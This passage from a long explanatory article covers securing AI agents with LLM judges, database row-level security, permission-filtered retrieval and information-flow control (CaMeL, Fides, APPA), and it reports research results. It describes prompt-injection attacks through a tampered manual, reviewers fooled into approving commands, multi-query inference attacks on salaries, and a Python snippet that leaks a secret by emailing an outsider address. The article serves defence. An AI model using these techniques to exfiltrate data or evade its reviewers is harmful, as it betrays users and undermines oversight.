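T is 2.425 / 3.0, or about 0.81, so the request passes at a threshold of 0.70 and fails at 0.85. If 100 requests had this score, with 95 legitimate and five from an attacker who had exploited the missing patch, a threshold of 0.85 would wrongly refuse 95 and a threshold of 0.70 would wrongly approve five. The stricter threshold is better only if one false approval does more harm than 19 false refusals. That may be true for pump settings and is probably not true for pump history, but the formula can't determine it.

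Averaging can also hide a warning. If the device specialist gave a trust score of 0 with a confidence of 0.5, T would be 0.75 and the request would still pass at the lower threshold. The confidence figures are the model's own estimates, and because all the specialists run on Llama 3.1, they may well make the same mistakes.

Roy and colleagues tested the system on 160 invented requests in a simulated military network, half of which it should have allowed. It decided 95% correctly, wrongly approving three of the 80 bad requests and wrongly refusing five of the 80 good ones. A plain program that applied the same policies as fixed rules got all 160 right in under a millisecond per request, while the agents took 46 to 134 seconds on a machine without a graphics processor.

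Roy and colleagues argue that agents can respond to new threats and adopt changed policies without anyone writing new rules. That could be an advantage, but this test can't show it because fixed rules settled every request. A fair test would use cases that fixed rules don't settle, like the bearings for 640.

Fleming, Kundu and Kompella (2025), in *Uncertainty-Aware, Risk-Adaptive Access Control for Agentic Systems*, use scores to decide when to involve a person. A model writes a policy for the new task and scores the risk of the tools the task needs and its own uncertainty. If either score exceeds its threshold (in their example, 8.0 out of 10 for risk and 0.6 for uncertainty), the request goes to a security officer. Isolating a hacked database requires a firewall change with a risk of 9.5, and the model's uncertainty is 0.75, so a person decides and the agent gets a token for about ten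 minutes. Posting a daily count of sales leads scores 3.0 for risk and 0.10 for uncertainty, so it goes ahead automatically.

The paper uses the highest risk score among the tools, so low-risk tools can't hide a high-risk one as they could in an average. The scores come from a list that the company maintains. The uncertainty estimate is weaker. One method the paper suggests is to ask the model several times and measure how much its answers differ, but a model that has misunderstood the task may give the same wrong answer every time. The paper reports no experiments.

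### Can the same text mislead the judge?

If a tampered manual can cause the agent to email pump history to a stranger, it might also cause a model reviewing the email to approve it. Fleming and colleagues leave this problem to future work, and Roy and colleagues didn't test it. Trębacz and colleagues found cases where testers misled OpenAI's reviewer into approving commands, and they don't expect such systems to offer firm guarantees.

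Anthropic's auto mode shows the reviewer only the user's messages and the proposed actions. It removes the results of tool calls, where planted text usually arrives, and the agent's own explanations, which might persuade the reviewer to make a bad decision. The reviewer would never read the manual, but it would see an email to an unknown company that the planner hadn't mentioned. However, it can't tell whether the agent found a job number in a database or made it up. Caper instead gives its reviewer shortened tool outputs and the observed effects, with instructions to treat them only as evidence. This exposes hidden harm, but it also lets an attacker's text reach the reviewer.

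In a test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, 19.03% of planted instructions succeeded against Codex with its checks off, and 5.83% succeeded with its reviewer on. The reviewer therefore stopped roughly 70% of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded, and the rest got past both the agent and the reviewer. None succeeded against Claude Code in auto mode, but only 0.09% did with its checks off, so that result reflects the agent more than the reviewer. OpenAI has since updated its reviewer.

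Protection is more dependable if the judge can block requests that a fixed policy allows but cannot override the policy's refusals. An attacker who completely fools such a judge can do only what the fixed policy already allows. Fleming and colleagues' judge lacks this limit because it writes the policy for a new task.

But a judge that can only refuse can't approve the bearings for 640 either. The utility first has to widen the fixed policy, for instance to allow up to 1,000 a month for bearings from any regular supplier. The judge would then refuse orders that don't fit the repair. Anything above the limit would go to the planner, who would see few enough requests to read them properly. If a tampered manual caused the judge to let unnecessary orders through, the utility could lose up to 1,000 a month.

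## How is an agent's access to databases and documents limited?

A gateway can easily check that an agent orders only two bearings, because the quantity is a separate argument of the call. Checking is harder when a tool accepts any query in SQL, the standard language of databases. One query can combine several tables and return thousands of rows, and the gateway may have no information about which of them the planner is allowed to read. The database can apply these limits itself, but only if it can identify the requester.

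### One account for everyone

Often the database can't identify the user behind an agent's request, because the tool server logs in with a shared account that can read everything. The limits on each user then exist only in the agent's instructions. Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026) warn in *Data Agents Under Attack* that users can simply ask such an agent for tables that their own accounts cannot open.

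The database accounts that agents use often have more authority than they need. *MAP* (Ma, Dai and colleagues, 2026) examined 254 public MCP servers for databases and found that the setup instructions for 81.5% of them requested more authority than the code used. The instructions for 47 servers requested full administrator rights, although 31 of those servers contained only operations that read or add rows. Administrators may have granted less than the instructions requested.

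To show the danger, the researchers gave a reporting server an administrator's login. Planted text then led it to delete a table of names and email addresses. The database's log recorded the deletion as an ordinary command from an authorised account.

### Do models respect permissions in the prompt?

*Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control* (Fei, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) tested how well models follow written permissions. The researchers created job roles for each of 53 databases from three public benchmarks. The prompt listed the columns and operations the role could use, and the model had to write a suitable query or refuse. The questions were ordinary and not designed to trick the model.

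| Model | Spider | BIRD | LiveSQLBench |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 2.6% | 10.5% | 17.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 4.9% | 7.7% | 13.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 10.9% | 21.2% | 35.3% |
| Snowflake-R1-7b (specialised in SQL) | 48.7% | 65.1% | 82.0% |

The figures are the share of requests in which the model broke the policy, and they rise from left to right as the databases get more complicated. They overstate the amount of data at risk, because a model was also counted as breaking the policy when it should have refused but instead answered a different question using permitted columns. Only about a third of GPT-5-mini's violations on BIRD used a forbidden column. Newer models may well do better than these 2025 ones, but even a 1% error rate is too high for payroll records.

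Leaving the forbidden columns out of the prompt reduced violations for some models but raised GPT-5-mini's from 12.7% to 26.8%. The model guessed the names of hidden columns about twice as often and answered more questions that it should have refused. Extra training on role policies cut one small model's violations on Spider from 50% to about 6%, but the model then wrongly refused 20% of all requests.

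A second model can check a query against the policy before the query runs. *Role-Conditioned Refusals* (Klisura, Khoury and colleagues, 2025) found that this improved refusals for four older models, though longer policies made every system tested less reliable.

Some policies depend on how a query uses a column. For example, a manager might be allowed to see the average salary but not any individual's salary. In *Policy-Conditioned Constrained Decoding for Column-Level Access Control in Text-to-SQL*, Miyamoto, Xin and Yamana (2026) put such rules in the prompt. Claude Opus 4.5 broke them in 20.4% of queries on one benchmark and 17.8% on another.

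Their alternative, PCC-SQL, limits which column names the model can choose as it writes a query. Whenever a column name comes next, PCC-SQL works out whether the name would appear in the output, a join between tables, a filter or a calculation such as an average. It then rules out the names that the policy forbids there. If no names are left to choose from, it refuses the request.

PCC-SQL had no violations with any of three open models, but it covers only a basic subset of SQL and needs access to the model's internal scores, which commercial services generally don't provide. Its queries also often gave wrong answers. With the largest model, they returned the right result for only 48.2% of the permitted questions on one benchmark and 18.2% on the other.

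Fei and colleagues conclude that the database should still enforce the permissions. A model that understands them is useful because it can avoid writing forbidden queries. When a model writes one, the database rejects it and the planner gets an error, even if a permitted query could have answered the question.

### Permissions inside the database

The utility can give the agent a separate database login for each planner it works for. The tool server uses the planner's verified token to choose the login, so nothing the model writes can change that choice. The database can then limit each login in several ways.

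The simplest limit is a database role that can read but not write. *SQL Query Engine* (2026) describes a system that does something similar by setting the connection to read-only, so the database rejects any command to change data. This is much safer than telling the model not to change data. But the agent's SQL may be able to turn off the read-only setting, whereas it can't give a role permissions that an administrator withheld.

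A view is a stored query that can be queried like a table. The utility could give the agent a view of the work orders that leaves out what each contractor charges. Column masking keeps the column but changes its values, for instance by showing only the last three digits of a phone number. An agent may mistake a masked number for a real one and try to call it.

Row-level security limits which rows each login may read or change. *Row Security Policies*, in the manual for the widely used open-source database PostgreSQL, explains that these rules apply in addition to ordinary permissions, so a login still needs permission to use the table itself.

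Some companies can't split a shared account, perhaps because old software depends on it. MAP, which Ma and colleagues built, offers them partial protection. It runs on the same machine as the database and the tool servers, and an administrator sets each tool server's highest permission level to read, write or administer. When a server sends a query, MAP identifies which program sent it and blocks the query if it exceeds that program's level. MAP added an average of 28 microseconds per query and reduced median throughput by 13.6%. It would have stopped the deletion in the demonstration, but it doesn't control which tables or rows a server may read.

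### One query, two planners

Suppose the utility's table of work orders has four rows.

| Order | Station | Pump | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| 881 | North | 4 | 480 |
| 882 | North | 7 | 150 |
| 883 | South | 2 | 900 |
| 884 | South | 5 | 300 |

A second table, `agent_stations`, lists the station that belongs to each agent login. In PostgreSQL, the policy could look like this:

```sql
GRANT SELECT, INSERT ON work_orders TO maintenance_agents;
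GRANT SELECT ON agent_stations TO maintenance_agents;

ALTER TABLE work_orders ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;

CREATE POLICY own_station ON work_orders
  FOR ALL TO maintenance_agents
  USING (station = (SELECT station FROM agent_stations
                    WHERE login = current_user));
```

The first line lets the agents read and add orders but not change or delete them. The policy limits the agents to rows whose station matches their login. It has no separate condition for new rows, so the same test applies to those.

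The agent now runs this query, once for planner P-117 at North and once for planner P-204 at South:

```sql
SELECT order_no, cost FROM work_orders WHERE cost > 200;
```

| Working for | Result |
|---|---|
| P-117 (North) | Order 881, cost 480 |
| P-204 (South) | Order 883, cost 900; order 884, cost 300 |

The database adds the policy's condition to each query. If a tampered manual led the agent to request every station's orders, the database would still return only North's to P-117's login. An attempt to add an order for South would fail with an error.

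The agents must not be able to write to `agent_stations`, or one could assign itself another station. PostgreSQL exempts administrators, and normally the table's owner, from row policies, so the policy would not restrict a server that logs in with one of those accounts. A view can also bypass the policy, because by default it reads the table with the permissions of the view's owner.

The agent also gets no notice that the results have been filtered. If P-117 asks for the total cost of all work orders, the agent gets 630 and may report it as the total for the whole utility, when the actual total is 1,830. The tool should therefore include a note in its reply that the result covers only North.

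*The Stochastic Deputy* (2026), which studies how to keep customers' data apart when agents query it, notes that PostgreSQL and SQL Server have built-in row-level security but MySQL doesn't. In MySQL, a team can build something similar from views that look up the user in a variable, but a query could change that variable because MySQL has no way to make it read-only. A company's existing database may therefore limit how well it can restrict an agent's access.

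### Fixed queries, cost limits and staged writes

The utility may not need to let the agent write SQL. A programmer can write the query in advance and leave gaps for values, as in "open orders above this cost". The model supplies only the cost, and the database treats it as a value even if it contains SQL commands. The tool server should fill in the station from the planner's identity, since the model could choose the wrong one. Fixed queries suit routine work, but they can't answer questions that nobody anticipated.

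Free-form queries also need a limit on the computing resources they use. Wang and colleagues give the example of a request to compare every customer with every similar customer, which could exhaust the memory of a database with 30 million customers without breaking any access rule. In one of their tests, an agent paired every row of one table with every row of another. Each table had 13.8 million rows, making about 190 trillion pairs, and the agent stopped responding for 30 minutes.

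The system in *SQL Query Engine* returns at most 50 rows by default. This limits how much data a single query can expose, but the database may have to read millions of rows to produce those 50. The utility should also have the database enforce a time limit on queries, and ideally run the agent's queries on a copy, so that a slow query doesn't delay staff using the original.

When an agent has to change data, it can write its proposals to a separate table, and an ordinary program or the planner can then copy the good ones across. The database can also count the affected rows before making a change final. If a command meant to correct one order would alter 4,000, the database can undo it. It can also mark rows as deleted and keep them for a month, which would have made an error like the Replit agent's easy to reverse.

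### Searching documents the planner may read

Much of what an agent reads is in manuals, reports and emails. In retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), a system fetches relevant passages and places them in the model's input. It usually finds them by their embeddings, lists of numbers that represent the meaning of a text. A vector database stores an embedding for each passage, and the search returns the passages whose embeddings are closest to the question's.

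A search that selects passages by closeness in meaning can return text the user isn't permitted to read, unless it also checks permissions. *LLM-enabled Applications Require System-Level Threat Monitoring* (2026) gives the example of a junior developer who asks about a project's financial risks and receives a passage from a restricted file on salaries. The file had a list of permitted readers, but the search did not check it. In *Securing the Agent* (2026), searches without a permission check returned other customers' data for 98% to 100% of test questions.

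The system can apply the permission filter before, during or after the search, and the choice affects speed and the quality of the answers. Suppose the utility has 100,000 passages and a contractor may read 1,000 of them. If the system finds the ten closest passages and then removes the forbidden ones, on average only 0.1 will remain, assuming permissions are unrelated to the topic. The contractor will usually get nothing, even though a permitted manual might contain the answer. To end up with ten permitted passages, the system would have to retrieve about 1,000 candidates.

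Filtering first works well for the contractor, because the system compares the question with only 1,000 passages. It is slow for an engineer who is allowed to read 90,000. A vector database is normally fast because its index lets it skip most passages, but a search restricted to an arbitrary set of passages can't easily use that index. *VADER* (2026) describes the third option, which checks permissions during the search.

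*Don't Stir the Pot! Authorized Vector Data Retrieval via Access-Aware Indexing* (2026) proposes building the index around permissions, with passages grouped by the roles that may read them. This is promising for a company with a few stable roles, though it would presumably take more upkeep if permissions changed every day.

Filtering after the search also has a security problem, because the search still includes forbidden passages. These can affect how long the search takes and how many results it returns, and an attacker may be able to learn something from either. If secrecy matters more than speed, the utility should filter before searching.

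### Stale permissions and shared indexes

Many systems copy each document's list of readers into the vector database when they index it. If a utility later withdraws a contractor's access to a report, the copied list may still include the contractor, and a search filter that works correctly would still let them retrieve the report. The system can avoid this by checking the original permissions on every search, or by updating both lists in a single step that either succeeds completely or changes nothing.

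*Beyond Similarity Search* (2026) compared a separate vector database with a design that stores embeddings and ordinary records together in PostgreSQL. The separate version needed about 1,800 lines of code to keep the two synchronized and had seven identified ways for them to become inconsistent. The combined version needed about 120 lines and had no such failure modes.

The same comparison measured leaks between tenants, meaning customers who share one system. In 1,000 queries, filtering in application code leaked twice (0.2%) because of a bug, while filtering in the database never leaked. A difference that small could easily be chance. The better argument for filtering in the database is that the rule applies to every query, including those from new code whose author forgot to add a filter.

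Database filtering can also be slow. *The Stochastic Deputy* warns of a sharp drop in performance when a user is allowed to read the data of a set of tenants. Keeping a separate index for each tenant avoids the filter but creates more indexes to maintain.

The utility should protect the embeddings of a confidential report as strictly as the report itself. An attacker who obtains the embeddings can test guesses about the text by running them through the program that created the embeddings. If the embedding of "pump 4 will close in May" is almost identical to a stored one, one of the utility's documents probably contains a similar sentence. *SoK* (2026), a survey of privacy risks in RAG, warns that weak login checks or wrong permission settings can expose embeddings and passages to outsiders.

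### What permitted answers can reveal

Suppose a policy lets an agent report total overtime pay but not what any one person earned. If only one of the six people on a utility's maintenance team works nights, the total overtime pay for the team's night workers reveals that person's overtime pay.

| Question | Answer |
|---|---|
| Total overtime for the whole team | 14,200 |
| Total overtime for the team, excluding night staff | 11,900 |

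Two permitted queries for total earnings can reveal what one person earned. If six people earned 14,200 in total and the five other than the night worker earned 11,900, the night worker earned 2,300. Row-level security doesn't prevent this because the totals have to include everyone's rows. Requiring each total to cover at least five people doesn't prevent it either, since these totals cover six and five.

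Filters can leak data in the same way. One rule that Miyamoto and colleagues tested lets a query use a column to select rows but not display it. A user could then ask for the names of everyone who earns more than 50,000, then everyone who earns more than 75,000. If salaries are whole numbers up to 100,000, each query can halve the range in which one person's salary lies, so 17 queries are enough to find the exact figure. Miyamoto and colleagues excluded attacks that use several queries from their study.

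Statisticians have known about these attacks for decades, but agents make them easier to carry out. Wang and colleagues tried two versions on six data analysis agents, including two commercial services. In one version, the attacker asked the questions one by one. In the other, the attacker made a single broad request and the agent planned the questions itself. Each agent was vulnerable, at least occasionally, to one or both versions.

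The database can add a random error to each total. If each error is at most 500 in either direction, the difference in the overtime example could be anywhere from 1,300 to 3,300, while the team's total would still be accurate to within about 4%. Differential privacy is the formal version of this method. Someone who repeats a question many times can average out the errors, so the system also needs to limit the number of questions.

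Wang and colleagues recommend that the system track everything it has disclosed during a session. This record should probably carry over to the user's next session, since an attacker could otherwise start a new session to clear it. Even then, two people working together could each ask one question and combine the answers.

An agent can also identify people by combining sources that are harmless on their own. Anonymous sickness figures might show that one person at North was ill in the first week of March, and the shift roster might show who was missing that week. *From Weak Cues to Real Identities* (2026) found that agents can identify people from such weak clues. Its safeguards reduced the problem but could also make the agents worse at legitimate work. The utility could stop any one task from reading both sources, but someone would have to anticipate the combination.

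*Protection Is Not One Event* (2026), a survey of RAG protections, points out that a system with no unauthorised retrieval can still disclose too much to an authorised user in its answers.

### Answers that outlast permission

Agents often store answers to save time. Zhou and Zhang note that a stored result can remain after the user loses access to its source. If P-117 moves from North to South on Monday, the database will block a new query about North's orders, but last week's summary may still be in the agent's memory.

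A shared store of answers can be worse, because it may match requests by their wording alone. If planners P-117 and P-204 both ask for open orders above 200, the second could receive the first one's answer without any query reaching the database.

The utility can prevent this mix-up by storing each answer under both the question and the planner's identity. In case the planner's access has since been withdrawn, the system also has to record which sources each answer came from and check the planner's current permissions on them before reusing it. This loses some of the time that reuse saves. For sensitive records it may be simpler to store nothing and run the query again.

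## How can untrusted text be kept from directing an agent or drawing data out?

Suppose the utility lets its agent read pump history and email Northfield Pumps to ask for prices. Each permission is sensible, but together they let the agent send Northfield the pump history, which nobody approved. An instruction planted in a manual could make the agent do this. A list of permitted recipients wouldn't stop the email because Northfield is on it. A ban on attachments wouldn't help much either, because the agent could write "vibration has doubled since March" in the message itself, and a filter would be unlikely to recognise that sentence as pump history.

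Unlike the previous two controls, information-flow control tracks where the message's content came from. It labels data, copies the labels to anything made from that data, and checks them before the agent sends something out or takes an important action.

### Two labels and a rule for combining them

In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), Costa, Köpf and colleagues give every value two labels. The confidentiality label lists who may read the value. The integrity label records whether the value is trusted, meaning it comes from a source an attacker can't write to.

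A value made from two others takes the stricter version of each label:

(R₁, t₁) ⊔ (R₂, t₂) = (R₁ ∩ R₂, t₁ and t₂)

Here R is the set of permitted readers and t is true if the value is trusted. If Ana, Ben and Chris may read the pump history, and Ben, Chris and Dev may read a contract, only Ben and Chris may read a report based on both. The report is trusted only if both sources are. Since nobody can reliably tell which words in a model's context influenced its answer, its output normally takes the combined labels of everything it has read.

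Two rules then cover most tool calls:

- An important action may go ahead only if everything that influenced the decision is trusted.
- Data may go only to people who are allowed to read it.

Suppose the planner asks the agent to find out why pump 4 is vibrating, create a work order and ask Northfield for the price of two bearings. The manual contains the planted line.

| Value | Who may read it | Trusted? |
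|---|---|---|
| The planner's request | Anyone | Yes |
| Pump 4's history | Utility staff | Yes |
| The manual from the supplier's website | Anyone | No |
| Anything the model writes after reading all three | Utility staff | No |

The model now proposes emailing the readings to Northfield. The call breaks both rules, because Northfield isn't on the list of readers and the manual may have influenced the decision.

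The utility needs both rules. With only the second, the manual could still cause the agent to order forty bearings, because the order discloses nothing confidential. But the same labels also block the work order and the harmless price request, since the model wrote those after reading the manual too. CaMeL and Fides both try to prevent the leak while still allowing the repair.

### CaMeL writes the plan first

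Google DeepMind's CaMeL keeps the manual away from the model that makes the decisions. It builds on a proposal by Simon Willison in 2023 to split an agent's work between two models. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe the design, which would handle the pump task like this:

1. A planning model reads the planner's request and nothing from outside. It writes the whole plan as a short program in a restricted form of Python.

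```python
history = read_history(pump=4)
manual  = fetch_manual(pump=4)
fault   = ask_reader("Which fault fits these readings?", history, manual)
create_work_order(pump=4, note=fault)
send_email("Northfield Pumps", "What do two bearings for pump 4 cost?")
```

2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the plan line by line and calls the tools. The planning model never sees the results.
3. At the third line, the interpreter passes the history and the manual to a second model, the reader. The reader has no tools and can only return a value, such as "worn bearing".
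4. The interpreter stores each value with a record of its sources and permitted readers. The value `fault` inherits the restrictions on both the history and the manual.
5. Before every tool call, a policy written as ordinary code inspects the arguments and these records, then allows or refuses the call.

Text in the manual can't add an email to the plan, because the plan was complete before the interpreter fetched the manual, but it can still make the reader return a false fault. If the planner had asked the agent to write to the contact named in the manual, the attacker could also have supplied the address. The policies are for such cases. One could reject any email address that came from a website. Another could require a trusted pump number on a work order but accept an untrusted note, which a technician will read before acting on it.

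In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL with two models on the banking tasks from AgentDojo, the prompt injection benchmark. With the policies off and no attack, CaMeL completed 67% of the tasks with one model and 71% with the other. With the policies on, it completed 37.5% with either model. Attackers succeeded in five of 622 runs with the policies off and in none of 588 with them on.

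The plan alone stopped nearly every attack. The policies stopped the last few but also blocked almost half the useful work. In about two thirds of the test cases, the attack needed a tool that the plan for the user's task would never call. The policies would probably matter more against an attacker who knows the design and plants a false account number instead of an instruction.

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stops nearly all of AgentDojo's attacks at comparable task performance. When Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL, its task performance was comparable only with its policies turned off. However, they were testing a rival to their own system, on only 16 tasks with three attempts at each.

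CaMeL finds a forbidden call only when the plan reaches it, after earlier calls have already run. Nikolaou and colleagues extend CaMeL by checking the whole plan before it starts. Their system maps the plan's possible steps and searches the map for a path that breaks a rule, such as "no pump shutdown without an earlier approval". If it finds one, it sends the path to the planning model, which can repair the plan. The check assumes that a loop may run any number of times, so it sometimes rejects a safe plan.

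*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) recommends a stricter language than Python, whose error handling makes data hard to trace. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapts the design to agents that operate a computer through its screen. The planning model has to write one plan in advance, with branches for what might appear there.

### Fides lets the agent look, at a price

Fides, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, lets the model choose its next step after each tool result, as an ordinary agent does. It keeps a label for the model's context and updates it as the context changes. When a tool returns text with a stricter label than the context's, such as the manual, Fides stores the text in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name.

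The model then has three options:

- It can pass the variable to another tool without reading it.
- It can have a separate model without tools answer a question about the text. The answer goes into a new variable.
- It can inspect the variable. The text then joins the context, the context takes on the text's labels, and Fides blocks later calls that require a trusted context.

The second and third options can be combined. The model can run a query on whether the manual mentions bearing noise, restrict the answer to yes or no, and inspect only that answer. Fides can record the answer's type in its label, so a policy could allow an untrusted yes or no where it would block free text. This lets an agent change its plan based on what it finds, which CaMeL's planning model can't do.

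Costa and colleagues tested Fides on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. Of the planted instructions, 152 succeeded against an ordinary agent, 21 against Fides without policies, and none against Fides with policies. AgentDojo's automatic scoring counted three successes in the last case, but the researchers judged that these were not real. The table gives the share of tasks each agent completed when there was no attack.

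| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent, with labels and policies | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| Fides, with policies | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The policies cut the ordinary agent's average score across the four settings, weighted equally, from 84% to 42%, and Fides recovered only 8 of the lost points. The travel policies rarely blocked anything, so Fides's losses there came mainly from GPT-4o's trouble with variables. Fides's travel score rose to 68% with o1, a stronger reasoning model.

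The perfect security result is partly due to how the researchers labelled the data. They marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, but a real company has no list of the fields attackers will use.

### What noninterference guarantees

Noninterference is the strictest guarantee information-flow control can offer. A program has this property if changing only its secret data never changes the results an outsider sees. The integrity version requires that changing only the untrusted text never changes anything marked as trusted.

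Fides offers explicit secrecy, a weaker guarantee than full noninterference. It covers data that the agent copies or rewrites, but not what an outsider can work out from the calls the agent makes. If the agent emails Northfield only when pump 4 is failing, the email's arrival reveals the fault, even if its text is harmless. Costa and colleagues argue that full noninterference would be too restrictive, because it would essentially forbid any publicly visible call after the agent had read something confidential.

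CaMeL tracks some of these indirect leaks but misses others. Garby and colleagues found a gap with a trick that dates from the 1970s. Adapted to the pump, it looks like this:

```python
leak = True
ok   = True
if vibration > limit: ok = False
if ok: leak = False
if leak: send_email("outsider@example.com", "Pump 4 is failing")
```

The vibration reading is confidential. When it is above the limit, the third line runs, and CaMeL marks `ok` as confidential. The fourth line then doesn't run, so `leak` stays true with its public label, and the email goes out. When the reading is normal, no email goes out. An outsider learns whether the pump is failing, although CaMeL detected no confidential data reaching the email. CaMeL also reruns failed plans from a loop outside the interpreter, where it tracks nothing. A program could extract a whole secret one bit at a time by repeating the trick.

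A planning model that isn't malicious is unlikely to write such code, and the attacker can't easily prompt it to. The gap is still good evidence that careful engineers can get the tracking wrong.

LLMbda, a programming language that Garby and colleagues designed for agents, attaches a label to every value and to every conversation with a model. A program can handle untrusted text in a separate conversation and then discard that conversation. LLMbda stops a program if a decision based on secret data would change a public conversation. CaMeL lacks an equivalent check for its variables.

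The researchers proved noninterference for every program written in the language without deliberate exceptions, including programs that a model writes during the run. They checked the proofs in Lean, a language for computer-verified mathematics. The proofs also cover the software that runs the agent.

The theorem permits one kind of leak, in which an outsider can learn something from whether the program finishes. Garby and colleagues show that if the program fails to finish with probability d₁ on one secret and d₂ on another, the visible results differ by at most (d₁ + d₂)/2 on a standard measure of distance between probabilities. With failure rates of 2% and 4%, the bound is 3%.

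The proofs assume that someone has labelled the data correctly and that every sensitive tool checks the labels. They also treat all data sources as part of the program, so they don't cover a real historian, whose data other software changes while the agent is working.

### Endorsement and declassification

Almost no useful agent can follow the two rules without exceptions. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes two kinds of controlled exception. Endorsement lets an agent treat a chosen piece of untrusted data as trusted for a defined purpose. Declassification permits a specified release of restricted data. For example, the planner might endorse the repair steps on one page of the manual after reading it. An engineer might declassify a week of vibration readings so that Northfield can help with the diagnosis.

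In Randori, Garby and colleagues' test agent, the planning model decides what to endorse while it writes the plan, before the agent has read any outside text. With labels always on, Randori completed between 65% and 75% of the banking tasks, depending on the model, and attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs. When the researchers removed endorsement, one model's completion rate fell from 75% to 62.5% and another's from 65% to 54%. These rates come from the same 16 tasks and could be off by about 20 points either way. A second theorem shows that endorsement in LLMbda can't expose secrets, however carelessly the agent uses it, though it can still lead to a bad payment.

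Declassification, or releasing data to someone outside its list of readers, is safer if untrusted text can't trigger it. Costa and colleagues describe a policy that allows such a release only when the decision came from a trusted context. Under this policy, the agent can email Northfield the readings if the planner tells it to, but not if it has read the untrusted manual first.

Even a short answer from untrusted text can be risky to trust. A yes or no carries only one bit, too little to hold an instruction, but it can still settle an important decision. At the utility, the question might be whether pump 4 can safely run without its vibration alarm, and a false "yes" from a tampered manual could wreck the pump. Zhou and Zhang conclude that a system should check whether a source has the authority to decide the question, however short its answer.

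Short answers can also leak data when combined. A choice from n options carries log₂ n bits, so ten choices from lists of eight carry 30 bits, enough to identify any nine-digit account number.

### When the next step depends on a document

If the planner asks the agent to do whatever checks the manual recommends, CaMeL can't write the plan in advance. Fides can read the manual, but it may then block the creation of the work order. Costa and colleagues found that about 43% of AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks have a next step that depends on the data, compared with 5% of office tasks and 10% of travel tasks.

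*SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) measures how much label checks reduce task completion for an agent that plans first and remembers results between requests. Suppose a user asks the agent on Monday to save an invoice and on Tuesday to pay it. SPA keeps the invoice's labels overnight and shows Tuesday's planning model only a description of what it stored, so an instruction planted in the invoice can't reach that model from memory. On AgentDojo, the label checks cut successful attacks to zero, but the share of tasks completed fell from 53.0% to 29.0%. Most of the loss came from legitimate plans that used outside data in an important action.

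Other designs reduce task completion about as much. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) lets a model keep its tools after reading untrusted text but restricts how it may use them. Garby and colleagues report that this design completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks without policies and eight with them, while CaMeL completed seven with policies. The similar losses suggest that much of the difficulty comes from the tasks themselves.

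Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, argue that such comparisons are unfair because they set an agent that has to stop at every blocked call against an undefended agent that may do anything. In practice, companies often make a person approve important calls, so the researchers counted how many tasks an agent could finish without approval.

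The agent Prudentia builds on Fides. It tells the model which labels and rules apply, and asks it to justify reading hidden text and to list the tool calls it expects to make afterwards. The model can also ask the user to endorse the text. If an email contains ten harmless errands, the user can endorse it once instead of approving each errand.

| Agent (all using o3-mini) | AgentDojo tasks finished with no approvals |
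|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, with approval for every important call | 24.3% |
| Ordinary agent with labels | 35.5% |
| Fides | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | 59.1% |

This answers the claim that labels only get in the way well, but it is less convincing on security. Kolluri and colleagues assume that people would refuse any call that came from an attack, whereas Hossain and colleagues' volunteers often approved unsafe requests. Endorsement also makes each decision more consequential, since a user who misses the planted line in that email frees the agent to act on it without further questions. Kolluri and colleagues gave Prudentia no matching shortcut for declassification because whether private data may go out depends heavily on the situation, which approving a single call takes into account better.

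### Labels that only get stricter

Under the combining rule, labels can tighten but never loosen. An agent that reads a maintenance report, a shift roster and a web page may end up with a context that only the planner may read and that can't support any important action. This buildup of restrictions is called label creep. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) used simulations to test whether better system design could prevent label creep. The system's size and how it distributed tools made a large difference, but design alone couldn't fully prevent the loss of useful work.

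Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026) prove in *APPA* that once labels have blocked a release, further reading cannot unblock it. Their system therefore gives the agent other options, including a temporary branch. To use a manual, for example, the agent opens a copy of its conversation and fixes a form in advance, with fields such as a part number and a fault chosen from a list. The branch reads the manual and fills in the form, then APPA discards everything else so that the manual's text never enters the main conversation.

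A hijacked branch can still choose the wrong fault from the list, so the utility has to decide whether to trust the form. It also can't recall any email the branch has already sent.

The agent can also request an exception for one exact call. A person, a fixed rule or another model may grant it within limits that the company sets, and the labels stay unchanged for the next call. APPA also works out how a call would change the labels before the call runs. This matters for a tool that reads pump history and emails it in a single step, because a check based only on what the agent has already read would allow the email.

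No attack succeeded in 1,320 test runs with APPA's protections on, and the agent completed between 64% and 91% of its tasks, depending on the model and test. One model completed 88% of the team's own set of office tasks, but 56.5% without branches and 35% without APPA's suggestions for getting past a block. These drops are good evidence that the recovery methods work. The comparison with Fides is weaker evidence, because the team set up Fides themselves, without several of the rules that the office tasks tested.

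Labels also spread too far when an agent uses a command line. A script might read one file or a thousand, and a cautious system would have to assume it read every file it could. *Flowsh* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) tracks which files a command opens and what it downloads, and combines only those labels. It stores labels with the files, so a summary of confidential pump history is still labelled confidential in next week's session. It holds back changes to files until the command has finished, then applies them if the labels allow it. Otherwise, it asks the user about the actual changes. It checks network requests before sending them because it can't recall them afterwards.

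Flowsh needed 5.8 times fewer approvals per completed task on office work, and 22.5 times fewer on a programming benchmark, than a permissive sandbox that requests approval for every action it can't show to be safe. But Flowsh's task completion rate was 8 to 10 percentage points lower.

### Wrong labels

All these systems can fail if the labels are wrong. Suppose the utility marks its historian as trusted, although a contractor can type comments into it. An instruction planted in a comment would then pass every integrity check. If the utility marks all email as untrusted, the agent can't act on the station manager's emailed instructions without an exception.

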